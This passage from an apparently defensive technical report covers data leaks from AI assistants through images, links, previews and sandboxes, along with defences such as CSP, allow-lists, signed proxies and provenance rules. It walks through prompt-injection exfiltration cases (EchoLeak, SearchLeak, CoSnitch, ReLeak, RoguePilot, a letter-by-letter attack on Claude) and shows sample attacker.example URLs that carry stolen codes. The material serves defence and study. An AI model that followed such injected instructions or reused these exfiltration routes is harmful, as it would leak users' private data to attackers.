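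| Antigravity | November 2025 | Listed as a known issue, still leaking in June 2026 | Odson and Morris |

In four of the nine cases (Writer, NotebookLM, AI Studio and the log viewer), the vendor acted within days of the researchers going public, after weeks or months of little progress in private. The sample is small, and researchers are more likely to write about slow vendors, but the pattern suggests that the delay usually had little to do with technical difficulty.

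Older consumer chat products are now better protected against these leaks. WithSecure's *When your AI Assistant has an evil twin* reports that Google's Gemini assistant blocked automatic leaks through images, so the security company's researchers had to trick the user instead. Google was still shipping another product with the leak at the time. According to Archestra, this pattern recurs because each new chat interface turns on markdown to give designers good-looking headings, and the developers then rediscover the flaw. Products that restrict images have also leaked, in attacks such as EchoLeak, SearchLeak and ReLeak, which a later section covers.

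### Links and link previews

An attacker can also leak data through an ordinary link, but the user has to click it. In January 2024 Amazon fixed such a flaw in Amazon Q, its assistant for businesses, which could put the earlier conversation into a link to an attacker's site. According to Willison, Amazon stopped the assistant from producing links at all. Requiring a click is a weak safeguard because the model also writes the link's label, and the user can't tell from a label like "view invoice" what the address contains.

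Messaging apps can leak data through a link that nobody clicks. When someone posts a link in Slack or Discord, the service fetches the page to show its title and a picture, which Slack calls unfurling. If an assistant posts an attacker's link with private data in the address, fetching the page sends that data to the attacker, as Willison (2024) explains in a note on Rehberger's work. The developer of a Slack app can prevent this by setting `unfurl_links` and `unfurl_media` to false in each message the app posts.

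The risk grew as people began to use AI agents through messaging apps. PromptArmor set up a test page where people could check their own combination of agent and app, and found that OpenClaw, a popular agent, was exposed by default on Telegram. TechNadu's *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* reports that the researchers also found the problem in Slack, in Discord, and in Microsoft Teams with agents built in Copilot Studio. Archestra lists Slack AI, Slack's own assistant, among the products whose makers have had to fix a version of the markdown leak.

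| What the model writes | What sends the request | What the user has to do |
|---|---|---|
| An image in a chat answer | The user's browser or app | View the answer |
| A link in a chat answer | The user's browser | Click the link |
| A link in a message on a service with previews | Often the messaging service's server | Nothing |
| An image in an email | The mail program | Open the email |
| An image in a saved conversation | The browser of the developer reading the log | Nothing |

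The second column determines which defences can work. A CSP on the chat page can stop the user's browser from loading an image, but it has no effect on a request from a messaging company's server. In that case, the agent's developer has to turn off the preview or remove the link before posting the message.

### How readily models write the image

Most demonstrations show only that the attack worked at least once. Two research projects studied it more systematically.

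*Imprompter* (Fu and colleagues, 2024) tested whether an attacker could disguise the instructions. A prompt that openly asks a model to put keywords from the conversation into an image address would alert anyone who read it. The researchers rewrote such prompts as strings that mix words from several languages with stray punctuation. These strings look like nonsense but have the same effect. Willison describes how an attacker could trick a user into pasting one from a website that offers ready-made prompts.

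The researchers found these disguised prompts with an algorithm called Greedy Coordinate Gradient, starting from example conversations that were each paired with the image address they wanted the model to write. The algorithm used the model's internal weights to estimate which token substitutions would make that output more likely, tried some of them, kept the best and repeated. It needs a model whose weights are public, but earlier research had found that such prompts often work on closed models too. The attack worked on Mistral's assistant, Le Chat. Mistral then restricted the assistant's markdown images, which closed the leak without having to recognise the disguised prompts.

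Ghosh, Simkin and colleagues (2025), in *A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems*, measured how well the injected instructions persist inside a larger program. The researchers, from the chip company NVIDIA and the security company Lakera, tested NVIDIA's AI-Q Research Assistant, which searches documents and the web and writes a report in several stages. They inserted the attack directly into the search results, as if the assistant had found a poisoned page. An ordinary test combines whether the search finds the page with whether the model obeys it. This test left out the first question, so its results apply only to cases where the poisoned text has already reached the model.

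Two of their 22 scenarios tried to get a markdown image and a link into the report, one in medical research and one in financial analysis. The image's address had placeholders for the user's email address and the link's for an ID number, which the model had to fill in. Each scenario had 21 versions of the attack, and the researchers ran each version five times, which makes 105 runs per scenario. A second model, GPT-4.1, graded the output:

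- 1 if the links appeared with the user's details filled in.
- 0.5 if the links appeared with the placeholders unchanged.
- 0 if the attack failed.

The half mark matters because a model that copies a link without filling it in leaks nothing about the user except that the page loaded. It also means the average score is not a success rate, since an average of 0.5 could mean that half the attacks worked completely or that all of them produced an empty link.

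At least one attack got the maximum score in both markdown scenarios. In one successful run, the assistant gave the links their own section in the report and added that the instructions were non-negotiable. Across all the scenarios with poisoned sources, the attacks' average score fell from 0.38 after the assistant first summarised its sources to 0.17 in the final report, after it had revised the text. Rewriting seems to remove material that doesn't fit the topic, which helps, but developers can't rely on it.

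The researchers then added an instruction to the final stage telling the model not to include links or text unrelated to the topic. The average score fell by about half in the markdown scenarios and two similar ones, but at least one attack still scored 1 in each. The researchers did not measure whether the instruction also removed useful links, which could be a problem in a research report that needs to cite its sources.

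The grading is fairly reliable but tends to be slightly lenient to the assistant. On a sample of 99 final reports covering various attacks, GPT-4.1 matched a person's score exactly 76.8% of the time and was within half a point 98% of the time. Its average score was 0.27, compared with 0.30 from people. The test graded only the text of the report, so it shows how often a model writes the image, not how often a browser would load it. The assistant used a 2025 model with 49 billion parameters, and the best current models should follow such instructions less often.

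### Use by real attackers

In this section's cases, security researchers attacked their own accounts or test systems, or in one case a volunteer who had agreed to a live demonstration. None of the reports describes a theft from a real victim, and many of the injected instructions in the web crawl described earlier had aims other than stealing data.

The lack of known victims is weak evidence that nobody has used the attack. A successful leak looks like a normal answer with an invisible image in it, and the only complete record of the stolen data may be the log on the attacker's server. The victim's company might find the request in its network records, if it keeps them, but it would be one image request among thousands. A vendor can see more if it checks each image's address before the browser loads it. Rehberger thought that OpenAI's check, despite its gaps, should let the company monitor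 for attacks and notice patterns.

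## Controls on images, links and outgoing requests

Every leak in the previous section ended with a request to an outside server, so a program can stop the leak by blocking that request, without recognising the injected text. trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data*, a post on an independent blog, argues that this should be the main defence, because an attacker can phrase an instruction in endless ways but a developer can list the few servers a page needs. Microsoft (2025) makes a similar distinction in *How Microsoft defends against indirect prompt injection attacks*, calling a defence probabilistic if it only makes an attack less likely to work, and deterministic if it guarantees that a particular attack fails whatever the model writes.

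In experiments, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (*Silent Egress*, 2026) found that domain allowlists and redirect checks protected an agent considerably better than defences in the prompt. The strictest controls block all external content, while the loosest let the user or a messaging app's settings decide what loads.

### Showing no remote images

A page that never loads an image from an outside address can't leak data through one. The renderer can drop such images or show their addresses as plain text for the user to copy. Google stopped turning images and links into HTML in Vertex AI's Generative AI Studio after Rehberger's report, according to Embrace The Red.

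The user loses photographs, maps and charts from other sites. An application can still show its own pictures. In the shop's case, the model names a product and the application inserts the photo from the shop's server. An attacker might influence which photo appears, but no outside server receives a request.

The control protects users only on screens that apply it, and the phone app, notification emails and log viewer may each have their own renderer. It also doesn't cover requests made by the assistant's tools. Tenable's *Gemini Browsing Tool* describes an attack on Gemini that avoided Google's controls on images by using the tool that opens web pages. An injected instruction made the tool request an address containing the user's saved details and location. Google has since fixed the flaw.

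### Allowing only listed hosts

A product that needs some outside images can restrict them to servers on an allow-list, such as `images.shop.example`. The check has to examine the host that the browser will actually contact, and many simple text comparisons get this wrong.

| Address in the answer | Server the browser contacts | Careless test that accepts it |
|---|---|---|
| `https://images.shop.example.attacker.example/a.png` | One of the attacker's subdomains | Starts with `https://images.shop.example` |
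| `https://images.shop.example@attacker.example/a.png` | `attacker.example`, because the text before `@` is a username | Starts with `https://images.shop.example` |
| `https://attacker.example/images.shop.example/a.png` | `attacker.example` | Contains `images.shop.example` |
| `https://notshop.example/a.png` | `notshop.example`, an unrelated domain | Host ends with `shop.example` |

A URL parser avoids all four mistakes. It is safest to use the browser's own, because two parsers can disagree about an odd address:

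```js
const HOSTS = new Set(["images.shop.example"]);

function imageAddress(text) {
  let u;
  try { u = new URL(text); } catch { return null; }
  if (u.protocol !== "https:" || u.port) return null;
  if (u.username || u.password) return null;
  return HOSTS.has(u.hostname) ? u.href : null;
}
```

The function compares the whole hostname with the list and returns the parsed address, so the page loads exactly the address that the function checked. If the function returns `null`, the page should show no image.

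Look-alike letters are a risk when someone writes a list of domains. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, the documentation for a tool that lets Claude open web pages, gives the example of `amazon.com` spelled with a Cyrillic "а" and recommends using only ASCII characters in such lists. In Anthropic's tool, a listed domain also covers all of its subdomains, which is convenient but assumes that the domain's owner controls all of them.

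An allow-list blocks images from any site that nobody thought to add, and the developer has to maintain it. It also fails if an attacker can read the requests a listed host receives, and attackers have repeatedly found such hosts. A redirect can defeat the check too, because a listed server may forward the browser to an unlisted one.

### Setting a content security policy

A content security policy makes the browser enforce the list. The server sends it as a header with the page, on one line:

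```
Content-Security-Policy: default-src 'self'; img-src 'self' https://images.shop.example; connect-src 'self' https://api.shop.example
```

Here `'self'` means the page's own origin. The `img-src` rule covers images, and `connect-src` covers requests that scripts make while the page is open. `default-src` covers most other kinds of content, such as scripts and fonts, that have no rule of their own. Before each request, the browser checks the destination against the relevant rule. If the rule doesn't permit the destination, the browser doesn't send the request, so the attacker's server never receives it.

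The browser applies `img-src` to every image on the page, whether it came from markdown, raw HTML or a style sheet, so the policy still works if the markdown parser or sanitiser has a bug. Browsers also check the destination of each redirect, which the function above can't do. A site can ask browsers to report blocked requests, and a report of a blocked image from the chat page may be the operator's first sign of an attack. Microsoft used such a policy to fix the image leak in Bing Chat, according to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*.

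The user notices only the missing images, but the developer has to find everything the page legitimately loads. If the policy breaks the site, developers often loosen it with a rule such as `img-src https:`, which allows images from any server that uses HTTPS and so does not prevent this leak.

Only the browser enforces the policy, and only for the page that carries it, so it doesn't cover mail programs, native phone apps or tools that run on the company's servers. Generated apps in a frame from another domain need their own policy. The rules in the example don't cover clicks on links, because following a link loads a new page instead of adding content to this one.

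A permitted server can also make the forbidden request itself. If the shop's site has a service that downloads from any address it receives, `'self'` lets the page call that service, which then contacts the attacker. *EchoLeak* (2025), an analysis of an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, describes how researchers explored such a fetch through SharePoint, Microsoft's document-sharing service.

### Fetching through an image proxy

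An image proxy is a server that downloads images and passes them on to users. The page rewrites each image address to point to the proxy, so the outside server receives the proxy's IP address instead of the user's and none of the user's cookies.

An image proxy protects the user's privacy from an ordinary website, but a proxy that fetches any address still delivers stolen data. When the model writes `https://attacker.example/logo.png?d=KX7Q2M`, the proxy requests that address, and the attacker reads the booking code `KX7Q2M` in the server log. A strict content security policy doesn't prevent this leak, because the browser contacts only the proxy, which the policy permits.

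Signed addresses can change this. The program computes a tag from the address and a secret key, using a function called an HMAC, and puts the tag in the proxy's address:

```python
def proxied(url):
    tag = hmac.new(KEY, url.encode(), "sha256").hexdigest()
    return f"https://img.shop.example/{tag}/{quote(url, safe='')}"
```

The proxy recomputes the tag and refuses to fetch the image if the two tags differ. Nobody without the key can make a valid tag for a new address.

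Signing image addresses helps only if the program is selective, because a program that signs every image in the finished answer will also sign the attacker's. The program can sign the addresses in emails and documents before the model reads them. The address with the booking code then has no valid tag, because it didn't exist until the model wrote it.

Signing doesn't stop the one-address-per-letter trick that Rehberger used against ChatGPT, because an attacker can put all 36 addresses in an email and have the program sign them. To prevent this, the proxy can download every picture when the email arrives and show only the stored copies, so that the model's choice of picture causes no outside request. The company pays for the storage, and senders learn that their emails arrived. The proxy also needs the protections against server-side request forgery described earlier, because strangers choose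 the addresses it fetches.

### Checking where an address came from

Some assistants need to open pages that can't be listed in advance. The program can instead check where an address came from. If the address existed before the model received any private data, the model can't have written that data into it.

Claude's `web_fetch` tool, which opens web pages, follows a rule of this type, under which Claude can choose an address but can't make one up. The current rules are in Anthropic's *Web fetch 工具*, the Chinese edition of the documentation.

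| Where the address has appeared | Can `web_fetch` open it by default? |
|---|---|
| A user message | Yes |
| The result of a tool that the developer runs | Yes |
| An earlier web search or an earlier fetched page | Yes |
| Only the system prompt | No |
| Only Claude's own output | No |
| Only the result of another tool on Anthropic's servers, such as code execution | No |

The tool also refuses addresses longer than 250 characters. It rejects those that appear to contain a password or access key, unless that credential was in the system prompt or the text of a user message. An injected instruction to add the user's recent answers to an attacker's address fails because the completed address appears only in Claude's output.

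Two of the permitted sources give less protection than they appear to. When the tool launched in 2025, Willison pointed out that many applications paste untrusted content into the user message, so an address in a stranger's email can count as one the user supplied. A developer's tools may also return text that Claude wrote. For example, if a tool runs Claude's code and returns the printed output, Claude can print a new address and then open it.

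### The hole that Ayush Paul found

Another weakness of the rule was that Claude could follow links on pages it had already fetched. Willison (2026) described in *15th July 2026* how Ayush Paul used this against the consumer version of Claude, which keeps memories of past conversations.

Paul built a website that showed Claude a fake notice claiming that, to protect the site from abuse, AI assistants had to authenticate by giving their user's name. The notice also said that, because of the fetching tool's limits, Claude would have to browse to the user's profile letter by letter. The page listed a link for each letter, and each link led to a page with further links. The site showed the notice only to visitors identifying themselves as Claude's fetching tool, so a person checking the site would have found nothing odd.

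Every address Claude opened was a link on a page it had just read, so the rule allowed all of them. The sequence of links it chose spelled out the user's name, home city and employer, and Paul's server recorded that sequence.

dyb, a personal blog, calculates how much each step leaked. The pages had 27 links, for the 26 letters and a hyphen, so each choice carried log₂ 27, or about 4.75 bits. The name "ayush-paul" took ten fetches, and all the data came to roughly 30 characters and 30 fetches. A limit on the number of fetches would have reduced this. With Anthropic's `max_uses` setting at 5, the first fetch loads the starting page and the other four spell four letters. The limit applies to each turn, however, so the attack could continue after the user's next message.

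Anthropic told Paul that it had already found the problem internally, and didn't pay a reward. It fixed the problem by preventing `web_fetch` from following links in the pages it fetched.

Developers who use the tool through Anthropic's API should not assume that they have the same protection, since the documentation still lists fetched pages as an allowed source by default. A newer setting, `url_sources`, can turn sources off. This example goes in the tool's definition and requires the web search tool to be on as well:

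```json
"url_sources": {
  "client_tool_results": {"type": "none"},
  "server_tool_results": {
    "type": "only",
    "tools": [{"type": "tool_reference", "name": "web_search"}]
  }
}
```

With these values, Claude can open only addresses that appear in user messages or search results. It can't follow links from one page to the next, which is a significant limitation for research tasks. Developers should keep untrusted text out of the user message, because the setting treats everything there as coming from the user.

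### OpenAI's index of public addresses

OpenAI's rule depends on the wider web instead of the conversation. *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that OpenAI decided against a simple list of trusted sites because many legitimate sites redirect visitors elsewhere, and strict lists cause so many warnings that people learn to click through them.

OpenAI runs a crawler, which records public web addresses as a search engine does and has no access to users' conversations or accounts. Before ChatGPT automatically loads a page or image, the software checks whether that exact address is in the crawler's index. ChatGPT can load the address if it is there; otherwise, the software prompts ChatGPT to try another site or shows the user a warning. An address containing someone's booking code is very unlikely to be in the index. As far as Rehberger could tell, addresses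 that the user types count as safe for that conversation.

This would have made Paul's attack harder, because an attacker can't generate the links during the conversation and has to publish the pages first and wait for the crawler to record them. But according to Embrace The Red, OpenAI acknowledges in a technical paper that the same one-address-per-letter trick still works if the addresses are indexed. Rehberger notes that a larger blog probably has enough indexed pages already, and that an attacker could use thousands.

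Rehberger suggests caching each page for a few minutes, or refusing to open the same address twice in a session, so that an attacker can't reuse the page for a letter. This makes the attack harder but doesn't stop it, because an attacker could publish a separate page for each character in each position, such as "third letter is u". Sending the 30 characters that Paul obtained would take 27 × 30 = 810 pages, with no repeated requests. A cap on automatic requests in each conversation would directly limit how much data could leak, but it would interrupt long research tasks.

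The control also has to be applied everywhere, and OpenAI's earlier check was not. Rehberger warns that developers at a large company may not know such a safeguard exists. OpenAI claims only that the rule stops quiet leaks through the URL. The rule does not make a page's content trustworthy.

### Asking before opening a link

When the program can't tell whether an address is safe, it can ask the user. This suits links, which often have to send some data to be useful. OpenAI's help page *ChatGPT generated links* gives the example of a user who asks where to buy a car. ChatGPT might offer a link to a car search that ends in "London" because it knows that the user lives there. The link is useful, but opening it also shows the site where the user lives. ChatGPT asks for approval before opening some links, including every link to a website that has asked OpenAI not to catalogue it.

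A good warning shows the link's actual address in full, not the model's label for it, and makes the hostname easy to see. Even then, users may not notice leaked data in the address if it is encoded, because few people can read base64. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) describes a better version called Safe Url, which detects when a request would send a third party something the assistant learned in the conversation. It either shows the user that information and asks for confirmation, or blocks the request and tells the agent to find another way. It also covers navigation and bookmarks in Atlas, OpenAI's browser, and searches and navigation in Deep Research, its report-writing agent.

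A warning page for links protects users less if it exempts some domains. Google's Colab, a service for writing and running code in a browser, showed a page asking users to confirm before opening links, except links to Google domains. Embrace The Red points out that this exempted Apps Script, which lets anyone publish a small program on a Google address and which Rehberger had already used to demonstrate data theft.

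Asking users to confirm an address relies on them reading the warning and recognising their own data in it. They are more likely to do this if warnings are rare, so confirmation works best after a stricter automatic rule has handled most addresses.

### Switching off link previews

Web page controls don't affect link previews in messaging apps, so a bot's developer has to turn the previews off, as with the two Slack settings described earlier. For OpenClaw on Telegram, PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* gives the setting `linkPreview: false` in the Telegram part of OpenClaw's configuration file. After the change, PromptArmor's test server no longer received data.

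Turning off link previews removes the title and thumbnail, which matters little for most bots. But the setting covers only messages that the bot posts through that app. If a colleague copies the link into another channel, posting it there may still trigger a fetch. Where an app offers no such setting, the developer can remove links to unlisted hosts before posting. PromptArmor would like messaging apps to let people turn previews off for a single chat or channel, which would protect users whatever the bot's developer did.

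An attacker can also hide instructions in a preview's text, as Lan and colleagues showed for agents that automatically receive a preview of each address. An agent that reads previews should treat them like any other untrusted page.

### What the large providers report

Microsoft, Google, OpenAI and Anthropic each describe different deterministic controls on outgoing requests. Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025) covers the Gemini app and Gemini's features in Gmail and Docs. *Google Workspace's continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections* (Gavish, 2026) describes how Google updates those defences.

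| Company | Remote images | Links and page requests | The user's part |
|---|---|---|---|
| Microsoft | Blocks the known leak through markdown images | Blocks certain untrusted links | Approves and sends emails that Copilot drafts in Outlook |
| Google | Gemini does not display external images | Replaces suspicious links with "suspicious link removed" | Confirms some risky actions, such as deleting calendar events |
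| OpenAI | Loads automatically only if the exact address is in the public index | Applies the same rule | Sees a warning before an unverified link opens |
| Anthropic | Not covered in the `web_fetch` documentation | `web_fetch` opens only addresses from permitted sources | Can supply a refused address in a message |

Google's control on links follows fixed rules but is probabilistic in practice, because it relies on Safe Browsing, Google's service for identifying dangerous sites. Safe Browsing may miss a domain that an attacker has just registered. Gavish reports that Google manages its rules for addresses, user confirmation and combinations of tools from a central policy engine. Staff can therefore block a new attack by changing a setting, sometimes just a text pattern, without retraining a model. A text pattern may miss a reworded version of the same attack.

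In 2025, outside researchers reported an attack to OpenAI in which an email about a staff restructuring contained instructions for the assistant to submit an employee's name and address to a "compliance validation system". The attack worked in half of the tests with one particular user request. OpenAI argues against relying on input filters because they usually miss attacks like this, which are as hard to detect as a lie.

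These documents describe designs and don't measure how often the controls fail. The security company Checkmarx reports that it could leak data through injected markdown in both Microsoft Copilot Chat and Gemini, and that Microsoft did not commit to fixing an image-based leak in Copilot Chat that needed no click. A developer who builds on one of these companies' models gets few of these protections automatically, since most of them are in the companies' own chat products.

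### A test that developers can run

A developer can find out whether a product leaks by displaying a harmless address and watching for the request. The test needs a server that records every visit:

```python
from http.server import BaseHTTPRequestHandler, HTTPServer

class Recorder(BaseHTTPRequestHandler):
    def do_GET(self):
        print((self.client_address[0], self.path,
               self.headers.get("User-Agent")), flush=True)
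        self.send_response(204)
        self.end_headers()
    do_HEAD = do_GET

HTTPServer(("", 8080), Recorder).serve_forever()
```

The recorder needs a public address, because a messaging service can't reach a developer's laptop. It also needs HTTPS, which an ordinary web server in front of it can provide. Browsers often refuse to load an unencrypted image on an encrypted page, so without HTTPS the product could pass the test only because the browser blocked the image. If another server forwards the requests, the recorder will show that server's IP address unless the developer also logs the original one.

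Each address contains a canary, a random string that appears nowhere else, so the developer can match a request to the test that caused it. The string should be long, since web crawlers will find the server and try short paths. The developer then sends these texts to the page as if the model had written them, using a small program that imitates the model's streaming service. The test leaves out the real model because a refusal would hide a fault in the display code.

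| Form | Text to send |
|---|---|
| Inline image | `![t](https://recorder.example/7f3a/inline)` |
| Reference-style image | `![t][r]`, and on a later line `[r]: https://recorder.example/7f3a/ref` |
| Raw HTML image | `<img src="https://recorder.example/7f3a/html">` |
| Inline link | `[t](https://recorder.example/7f3a/link)` |
| Reference-style link | `[t][s]`, and on a later line `[s]: https://recorder.example/7f3a/reflink` |
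| Bare address | `https://recorder.example/7f3a/bare` |
| Split image | The raw HTML image in two pieces, cut in the middle of the tag |
| Unfinished answer | A complete raw HTML image, then a ten-second pause before the rest of the answer |

Each form needs its own test, because a product may handle one correctly and miss another. Odson and Morris describe an attack that told the agent to write the same image in five formats, since only one had to load. According to trackr.live, filters in Microsoft's products missed reference-style markdown in EchoLeak and HTML that was still streaming in SearchLeak.

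The test fails if an image request reaches the recorder. A link should cause no request until someone clicks it, and then only after any warning that the product is supposed to show. In the recorder's log, a browser's name and the tester's own IP address suggest that the request came from the page, while an unfamiliar server or a name such as "Slackbot" suggests a preview or a proxy. A broken recorder would also leave the log empty, so the developer should first open one of the addresses by hand in the same browser to check that the request is logged.

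The developer should repeat the test on every screen that can show an answer, including the phone app, notification emails, the log viewer and any messaging app. The test takes little effort, so the developer can run it before each release to catch an update to the markdown library that turns raw HTML back on.

A second round uses the real model. The developer puts a canary in a fake private record, gives the assistant a test document that asks for an image whose URL contains the canary, and watches the recorder. Any request counts as a failure, even if the canary is missing, because the model may have encoded the string or, as in Lan and colleagues' experiments, split it over several requests. Passing this round is weaker evidence than passing the first, because a test document with different wording might succeed.

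The request recorder can't test the allow-list because its own address isn't on it. For each permitted host, the developer has to check separately whether a stranger can open an account there, read its logs, make it fetch another address, or buy the domain if it expires.

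## Attacks that got past these controls

By 2025, several large products combined an injection filter, a link filter and a content security policy, and researchers still got data out of them. Most of the controls worked as designed, but each relied on an assumption that the researchers broke. Microsoft, GitHub and OpenAI had patched the seven main attacks in this section by the time the researchers published them.

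### EchoLeak and the Teams relay

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers an employee's question by searching the email, files and Teams chats that the employee can open, and adding relevant passages to the model's context. Outsiders can't query Copilot, but they can email the employee, and Copilot then searches that email along with everything else. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) describes how the security research team Aim Labs used this to steal data.

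The email first had to turn up in Copilot's search. Search systems of this kind often turn each passage into a list of numbers that represents its meaning, and return the passages closest to the question. A short email is close to few questions, so the researchers wrote a long one that the system would split into pieces. Each piece had a heading, such as a guide to leave of absence or to common HR questions, followed by the same instructions. An employee who asked about any of those topics could bring the instructions into the model's context.

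The attack then had to get past four controls:

1. A classifier scanned incoming text for prompt injection. The email addressed its instructions to the employee and never mentioned Copilot or AI, so it read like ordinary office correspondence.
2. A filter removed markdown links and images that pointed outside the company. It recognised only the inline form, and the email made Copilot use the reference form, which puts the address on a separate line.
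3. The page's CSP allowed images only from listed hosts, most of them Microsoft's. One of those hosts would fetch other addresses on request.
4. Copilot normally names the documents behind an answer, which could have exposed the email. The email told its reader never to refer to it, for compliance reasons, and Copilot left it out.

The researchers had to find a permitted host that would forward a request. A SharePoint service did so, but only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. They then found a Teams service that needed no invitation. The browser requested an image from Teams, which the policy allowed, and Teams sent the attacker's server a request whose URL contained the stolen text.

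The attacker didn't need to know what the company's files contained, because the email asked for the most sensitive information in Copilot's context. For the attack to work, the victim only had to ask Copilot an ordinary question.

The 2023 image leak in Bing Chat needed no click, though Ravia calls the later EchoLeak the first zero-click AI vulnerability. Willison, in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, describes EchoLeak as an extended variant of attacks already seen in a dozen products. Zenity Labs writes in its post *EchoLeak* that researchers had disclosed this path into Copilot almost a year earlier. Ravia is more convincing in the narrower claim that earlier attacks either required the user to point the chatbot at a malicious file or page, or could take only limited data.

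According to the academic analysis *EchoLeak*, Aim Labs reported the flaw in January 2025 and Microsoft finished a server-side fix in May. The flaw was published on June 11 as CVE-2025-32711. *EchoLeak* reports that Microsoft began removing reference-style links and images from incoming external content. It also recommends marking external text and telling the model not to obey it, which is only a probabilistic defence.

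### SearchLeak and the early image

A year later, the security company Varonis got data out of the same product by a different route, described in *SearchLeak* (2026). The attack began with a link to Copilot's enterprise search page, which accepts a query in the link so that colleagues can share searches. Copilot treated the query as instructions, so an attacker could use it to make Copilot look through the victim's email and write an image address containing what it found. Tools that block phishing links were unlikely to stop this one because it led to Microsoft's own site.

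To guard against dangerous HTML, Microsoft's page wrapped each finished answer in a code element so that the browser would display tags as text. But the page displayed the answer while it was still streaming, so the browser had already read an image tag in it and requested the picture by the time the page wrapped the answer.

The policy blocked images from the attacker's server but allowed them from any address on Bing. When Bing searches for pictures similar to one on the web, its servers download that picture from whatever address the request contains. The browser therefore contacted Bing, whose servers then contacted the attacker's. In the demonstration, the attacker's log contained the subject line of an email, which included a six-digit security code.

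Ravia's EchoLeak post had listed every image host Copilot permitted, including `*.bing.com`, so anyone looking for another relay could have started there. Microsoft fixed the flaw, CVE-2026-42824, in early June 2026, according to TechRadar's *Microsoft 365 Copilot can be turned into a one-click data theft tool*, and Varonis published its findings on June 15.

Varonis points out that the attack needed all three weaknesses, so fixing any one would have stopped it. A vendor can therefore close a report like this after one fix, leaving the other weaknesses for an attacker to combine with a new one.

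### Prompts that run from a link

Varonis researchers used a prompt in a link to attack the consumer version of Copilot. *Reprompt* (Taler, 2026) explains that Copilot checked the addresses it was about to fetch and could remove private data from them, but only on the first request. The researchers told Copilot to do everything twice and compare the results. In one test, the check removed a secret phrase from the first request, but the second went out with the phrase intact. The attacker's server could then reply with further instructions, each asking for different information, so nobody could tell from the original link what the attack would steal. Microsoft received the report in August 2025 and patched the flaw in January 2026, according to The Next Web.

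Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026) used a link to the consumer Copilot that filled in a prompt, which normally ran only if the user pressed Enter. The researchers repeatedly asked Copilot why a prompt couldn't run by itself, and its explanations included an undocumented link setting that was supposed to be disabled. When they added that setting to a link, the prompt ran as soon as the page loaded. It told Copilot to read a connected Gmail account, put the result in a web address and summarise the page at that address. Copilot's ordinary page-reading feature then sent the data by opening the address.

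CoSnitch could also plant instructions in Copilot's memory through a web page that the user asked it to summarise. These instructions survive a password change because they are tied to the account, not the session. Microsoft patched the flaws on August 18, 2026, about eight months after the report. TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot* lists them as CVE-2026-24301, with a severity of 8.8 out of 10.

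A link that fills in a prompt without submitting it is a reasonable convenience, since the user can read the text first. Users lose this protection if any other setting can submit the prompt. Even when the user must press Enter, a long prompt may hide its purpose, as invisible text did in the attack on Claude.ai.

### ReLeak's three ways out

Cato Networks bought Aim Security in September 2025, and the team that found EchoLeak went back to Microsoft 365 Copilot. Simonovich (2026) presented three new zero-click attacks in *ReLeak* on December 3. The team used AI agents to write and test malicious prompts, according to Infosecurity Magazine. An unopened email was again enough for an attack, and Punto Informatico's *ReLeak* reports that the instructions got past Microsoft's injection classifier by looking like legitimate requests.

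| Where Copilot put the data | What contacted the attacker's server | CVE number | Patched in 2026 |
|---|---|---|---|
| The address of a markdown image | Bing | CVE-2026-124115 | November 15 |
| A link inside a file it created | Microsoft's background processing of saved files | CVE-2026-124132 | November 11 |
| Python code that it ran | The code interpreter's sandbox | CVE-2026-78501 | September 17 |

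The image attack repeats the failure in SearchLeak, since a permitted Microsoft service again passed the request on. Fadilpašić (2026), in *Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot*, identifies the service as Teams, while Infosecurity Magazine and Punto Informatico identify it as Bing. Bing is more likely, because Infosecurity Magazine matches it to a specific CVE number and patch date. Neither Infosecurity Magazine nor Punto Informatico says whether it was the same image search that SearchLeak used.

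In the document attack, Copilot saved a Word, Excel, PowerPoint or PDF file containing a link with private data in its address, and Microsoft's servers later opened the link while processing the file. According to Pravda.ru, a Russian news site, the requests in Cato's tests arrived one to eight minutes after the conversation ended, although nobody had opened the file. The chat page's CSP doesn't apply to these requests because they don't come from the page. A developer who runs the recorder test from the previous section should therefore also have the assistant create files, and leave the recorder running well after the chat ends.

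In the third attack, Copilot ran Python code that sent the data directly out of the sandbox. According to Microsoft's documentation, the sandbox blocked outgoing traffic, but the researchers found ways around the block. Microsoft rated the flaw's severity 8.6 out of 10.

Amazon responded differently to a similar finding. The security company BeyondTrust reported in September 2025 that an Amazon code interpreter for AI agents allowed DNS look-ups in a mode that was supposed to have no network access. As in the ChatGPT case described earlier, code could smuggle data out in the names it looked up. The Hacker News' *AI Flaws in Amazon Bedrock, LangSmith, and SGLang Enable Data Exfiltration* (2026) reports that Amazon considered this intended behaviour and told customers who need full isolation to use a different mode. Customers therefore can't rely on the name of a "no network" setting and have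 to test what it blocks.

### Fetches that start in a style sheet or a schema

Attackers can use any feature that downloads something automatically the way they use an image. Copilot could also preview HTML files it had written, and the preview removed image tags. Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* describes how Rehberger got past this filter with a style sheet that gave the page a background image from an outside server, and the browser fetched it. The flaw is CVE-2026-24299.

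A coding assistant has also leaked data through a JSON file. A JSON file can include the address of its own schema, and some editors download that schema to check the file. The Hacker News' *RoguePilot Flaw in GitHub Codespaces Enabled Copilot to Leak GITHUB_TOKEN* (2026) describes how Orca Security exploited this in Codespaces, GitHub's online development environment. The attacker hid instructions in a comment inside a GitHub issue. When a developer opened a codespace from that issue, Copilot automatically received the issue's text as a prompt. The instructions made Copilot check out a proposed code change containing a symbolic link to an internal file, read the file, and put the access token it found there into a schema address, so the token leaked when the editor requested the schema. Microsoft has patched the flaw.

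### Spelling with fixed addresses

A filter that refuses every address the model has written or altered can still leak data, because the model can send information by choosing among fixed addresses. Rehberger demonstrated this method against ChatGPT in 2023, and the two attacks below used it against stricter rules.

If the attacker supplies ten addresses, one for each digit, each request leaks one digit (log₂ 10, or about 3.32 bits), and six requests in order can reveal any six-digit login code. Each address is harmless by itself, so a filter that inspects one address at a time does not detect the leak.

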